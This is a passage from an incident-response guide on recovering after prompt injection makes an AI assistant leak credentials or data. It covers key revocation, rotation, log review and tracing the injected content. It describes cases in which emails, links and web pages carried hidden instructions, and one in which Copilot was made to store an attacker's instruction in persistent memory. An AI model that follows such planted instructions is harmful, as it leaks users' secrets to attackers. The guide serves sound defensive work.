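The first step is to revoke the credential, without waiting for proof that somebody has used it. In the Dragos test, thieves tried some stolen keys within hours. At the same time, the organisation should disconnect the assistant from the affected data, because an injected instruction still in place could leak the replacement credential.

Revoking a key can stop every program that depends on it, and GitGuardian thinks this is why many teams do nothing. If a service allows two keys at once, the team can create a new one, switch the important programs to it and revoke the old one minutes later. Kenney and colleagues recommend recording each credential's owner, permissions and replacement procedure in advance, and practising the procedure. Deleting the message or file that contained the key is not enough, because the attacker already has a copy.

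Other secrets need different treatment:

- For a password, end all open sessions as well as changing it.
- For a signed link, find out whether the service can cancel it. If not, replace the key that signed it, or move or delete the file.
- For source code, search the stolen files for credentials and revoke those.
- For personal data, tell the people affected what leaked. The law may also require a report to a regulator.

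The second step is to put the new credential into every program that needs it and remove the old copies, which may be in several places on one computer. The new credential should have only the permissions it needs, and the assistant should not be able to read it.

The team should then check how anyone used the old credential, starting from the earliest possible leak, not the day somebody noticed it. The service's logs may show access from unfamiliar networks or large downloads. The team should also look for new users and keys, because a thief who created a second key can keep using it after the owner revokes the first.

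Finally, the team needs to find the content that carried the instruction, starting with any records of what the agent had read. The assistant's citations may not help. Slack AI's citations, for example, did not include the attacker's message. For Copilot Cowork, PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* lists skills, emails and Teams messages among the possible sources. If the records show no suspicious document, the instruction may have been in a link, as in SearchLeak. In that case, the team should also search browser histories for links to the assistant with unusually long queries.

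The assistant's saved memory needs a separate check. In another part of the CoSnitch research, Varonis showed that a web page could make Copilot save an attacker's instruction and apply it in every later conversation. Changing the password or ending all sessions did not remove the instruction, so the user had to delete it in the memory settings. Microsoft has fixed the flaw, but a fix does not necessarily delete instructions already saved.

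Once the team finds the source, it should keep a copy as evidence and remove the original from everything the assistant can search. It should then look for other people who received the same email or file, because their assistants may have leaked something too.
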